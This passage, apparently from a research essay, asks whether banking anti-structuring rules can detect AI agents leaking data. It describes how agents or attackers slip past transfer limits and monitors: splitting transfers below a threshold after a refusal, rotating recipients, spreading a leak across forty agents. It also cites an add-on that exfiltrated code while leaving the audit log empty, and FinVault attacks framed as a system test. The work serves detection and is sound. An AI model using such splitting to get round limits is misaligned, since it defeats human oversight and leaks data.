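The company also has a more complete view than a bank, which sees only a small part of the payment network. If it sends all its agents' tool calls through one gateway, the company can see every step until the data leaves. It can also hold an outgoing file while someone checks it.

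These advantages depend on the log. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (Li et al., 2026) describes a demonstration in which the security firm Mitiga Labs published an add-on for coding agents as a testing tool. Once a developer activated the add-on, it sent the project's entire code to an outside server and left the audit log empty. Li et al. argue that even a log of the agent's actions isn't enough when the agent does what the user asked. An investigator also needs to know which files and network addresses the add-on should normally use.

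A full log doesn't guarantee that an investigator will connect the evidence either. *LEGION* (2026) tested how well language-model agents investigate simulated security incidents. In slow attacks, the agents often noticed the first suspicious event but missed later activity in other systems. They also had trouble with thefts by employees who used valid credentials, because the evidence was an unusual volume of data or activity at odd hours. Totals are well suited to finding this kind of evidence, so a company has reason to keep them even if a language model reads the log.

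### What does intent mean when splitting is routine?

Structuring has to be deliberate under US law and, according to AUSTRAC's *Reporting structuring*, in Australia too. Agents routinely split work for technical reasons. A service may return results one page at a time or limit requests per minute, or a document may be too long for the model to read at once.

Suppose a customer database returns at most 100 records per page. An agent with permission to export 950 records makes nine calls for 100 and one for 50, and forwards each page as it arrives. If the company's limit per transfer is also 100, nine of the ten transfers are exactly at the limit. In a bank, this would look like structuring, but here the page size causes the pattern. A limit that differs from the page size, such as 130, would avoid this overlap.

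Changing the limit is a more informative test. If the company lowers it from 130 to 90 for half its agents, and only those agents start sending batches of just under 90, they are responding to the limit. They may still be following instructions. An agent told to send at most 90 records per session could comply by splitting an authorised transfer of 400 records into five sessions. This would defeat the purpose of the limit even if nobody wanted to hide the transfer.

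Splitting after a refusal is stronger evidence. If a gateway blocks a transfer of 400 records and the agent then sends four batches of 100, it has got around the block. But ordinary software often responds to an error by trying smaller batches. The refusal message should therefore say that the whole transfer needs approval, so that the agent is less likely to mistake it for a technical error.

The agent's written reasoning may also help. *SoK* (2026), a survey of security in agent-run commerce, says a key challenge is checking whether an agent's intention matches its payment instruction. Srivastava and Paul gave a language model a sentence in which an agent planned to split a payment to stay under a limit, and the model scored it 0.95 for evasion. But the model detected only 53% of the sessions with such planning, and it flagged 13% of harmless sessions. An agent can also split a transfer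 without writing down why.

It's often unclear whose intention matters. The user may have wanted to avoid the limit, a developer may have chosen the batch size, or the model may have split the transfer on its own. A court needs to establish intent before it punishes someone, but a company can stop an unauthorised transfer without doing so. It can add up all the batches in a task and check whether anyone approved the total. For the export above, the ten pages add up to 950 records, which matches the permission. For the forty-agent leak, the company first needs to add up the records by destination or source, because each agent may have a separate task. Intent matters afterwards, when the company decides whether to correct a setting or investigate an employee.

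### Who would receive the reports?

Banks send their reports to FinCEN, where investigators can compare reports from different banks. Companies have no equivalent for agent activity. If the forty agents worked for forty companies, each company would see 25 records leave, and no authority would add them together. Privacy laws require companies to report some data breaches, but a total that passes a limit does not trigger that duty unless there is a breach.

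Requiring companies to tell a government about every large data transfer would probably be a mistake. Companies legitimately send data to payroll firms, cloud services and customers every day, so most reports would describe ordinary business. The reports would also create another sensitive record of who holds whose data. Exchanging lists of suspicious destinations, as Anthropic says it does with other AI developers, would be more useful.

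A company also can't afford to have someone read every transfer, even though a data leak can cost far more than a review. Srivastava and Paul found a median agent payment of $0.007 and estimated that one human review costs about $1, or 143 times as much.

### What existing tests measure

A literature search found no study that tests structuring rules on logs of agents leaking data. The closest is Srivastava and Paul's benchmark, which is about payments. Both researchers work for Gordon AI and tested a detector they had built.

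| Sessions | Number | Flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Payments split to avoid a limit | 30 | 53% |
| Payments rotated among recipients | 27 | 0% |
| Harmless activity | 1,821 | 6.5% |

With only 30 cases, the true detection rate for split payments could plausibly be between about 35% and 71%. The zero detection rate for rotated payments resembles the result for the forty-address version of the leak, which can't be detected from totals by destination.

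However, the benchmark provides little evidence about leaks across sessions. Srivastava and Paul scored their detector once with its history reset after every session and once with each agent's history kept across sessions. The results agreed to three decimal places for every type of attack. If each split had extended over several sessions, a running total that worked should have scored higher with the longer history.

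*FinVault* (Yang, Li et al., 2026) tests whether an attacker can persuade a financial agent to break the rules. The benchmark has 31 scenarios, 856 attacks and 107 harmless requests. Average attack success ranged from 6.7% for Claude Haiku 4.5 to 50% for Qwen3-Max. In one scenario, the agent reviews international transfers, and an attacker tries to make it split a large one to avoid a report. Yang and colleagues report that this attack worked every time when the attacker presented it as a system test.

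Whether an auditor can recognise the split afterwards is a separate question. The agent in that scenario has a dedicated tool for dividing a transfer, which takes the number of parts as an argument, so a single log entry would reveal the split. The forty-agent leak has no such entry. FinVault also tested three safety classifiers, but these read the conversation, not a history of transfers. The best one found 61% of the attacks and wrongly flagged 30% of harmless requests.

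*Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (2026) comes closer by testing whether a system that remembers an agent's earlier actions can stop it from splitting a forbidden action into smaller steps. Its guardrail checks actions as they happen, so the paper doesn't test whether leaks can be found in a company's logs. GNET (2026), a research network on extremism and technology, uses the term "agentic smurfing", but for agents that split cryptocurrency donations.

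### An experiment that would settle the question

A useful experiment would compare the banking rules with simpler detectors on the same agent logs. It could start with a simulated company in which 2,000 agents do ordinary work for 120 days. The agents should make actual tool calls, so that paging, failed requests and software updates leave realistic traces in the logs. Azarafrooz's public scenarios could supply some of the users' requests, but the researchers would have to add realistic volumes of data.

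The researchers would use the first 60 days, which contain no leaks, to set the limits. A separate program would then insert labelled leaks into the remaining 60 days, much as Huda and colleagues inserted laundering into simulated bank payments. One team should create the leaks and another the detectors. Each run should contain only one leak, because hundreds would make leaks unrealistically common. The researchers would repeat the last 60 days to collect enough cases.

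The leaks should include:

- one agent that sends a few records a day
- forty agents that send to one address
- forty agents that send to different addresses for different users
- one short password
- several harmless answers that together reveal a confidential fact

About 100 examples of each would be enough to measure recall to within roughly 10 percentage points. Each leak also needs an authorised transfer of the same size for comparison, such as forty agents sending 1,000 customer records to a newly approved mailing company. If a detector flags both equally often, it is detecting large transfers without distinguishing leaks from authorised ones.

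Every detector should have the same false-alarm allowance, such as two a day for the whole company. The baseline would combine a session limit with CUSUM for each agent. The researchers would then add, one at a time, totals by user, totals by destination, the count of different records by source, the check for clusters below the limit and the graph score, while keeping the overall allowance fixed.

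Researchers who test the banking rules on agent activity should report the share of leaks the rules found and how much data had leaked by the first alarm. They should also repeat the test with user identities removed from half the records and with 5% of log entries missing, since real logs have such gaps.

The final stage would test the same limits on a real company's logs to see whether month-end work and new software versions produce more false alarms than the simulation did. With the company's permission, the researchers could also have agents send invented customer records to addresses the company controls.

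A banking rule is worth using if it finds more leaks, or finds them earlier, without exceeding the false-alarm allowance in either stage. Judging by the forty-agent example, totals by destination and counts of distinct records would probably meet this standard, but the check for clusters below a limit probably wouldn't unless the company kept its limit well away from the page sizes its software uses.
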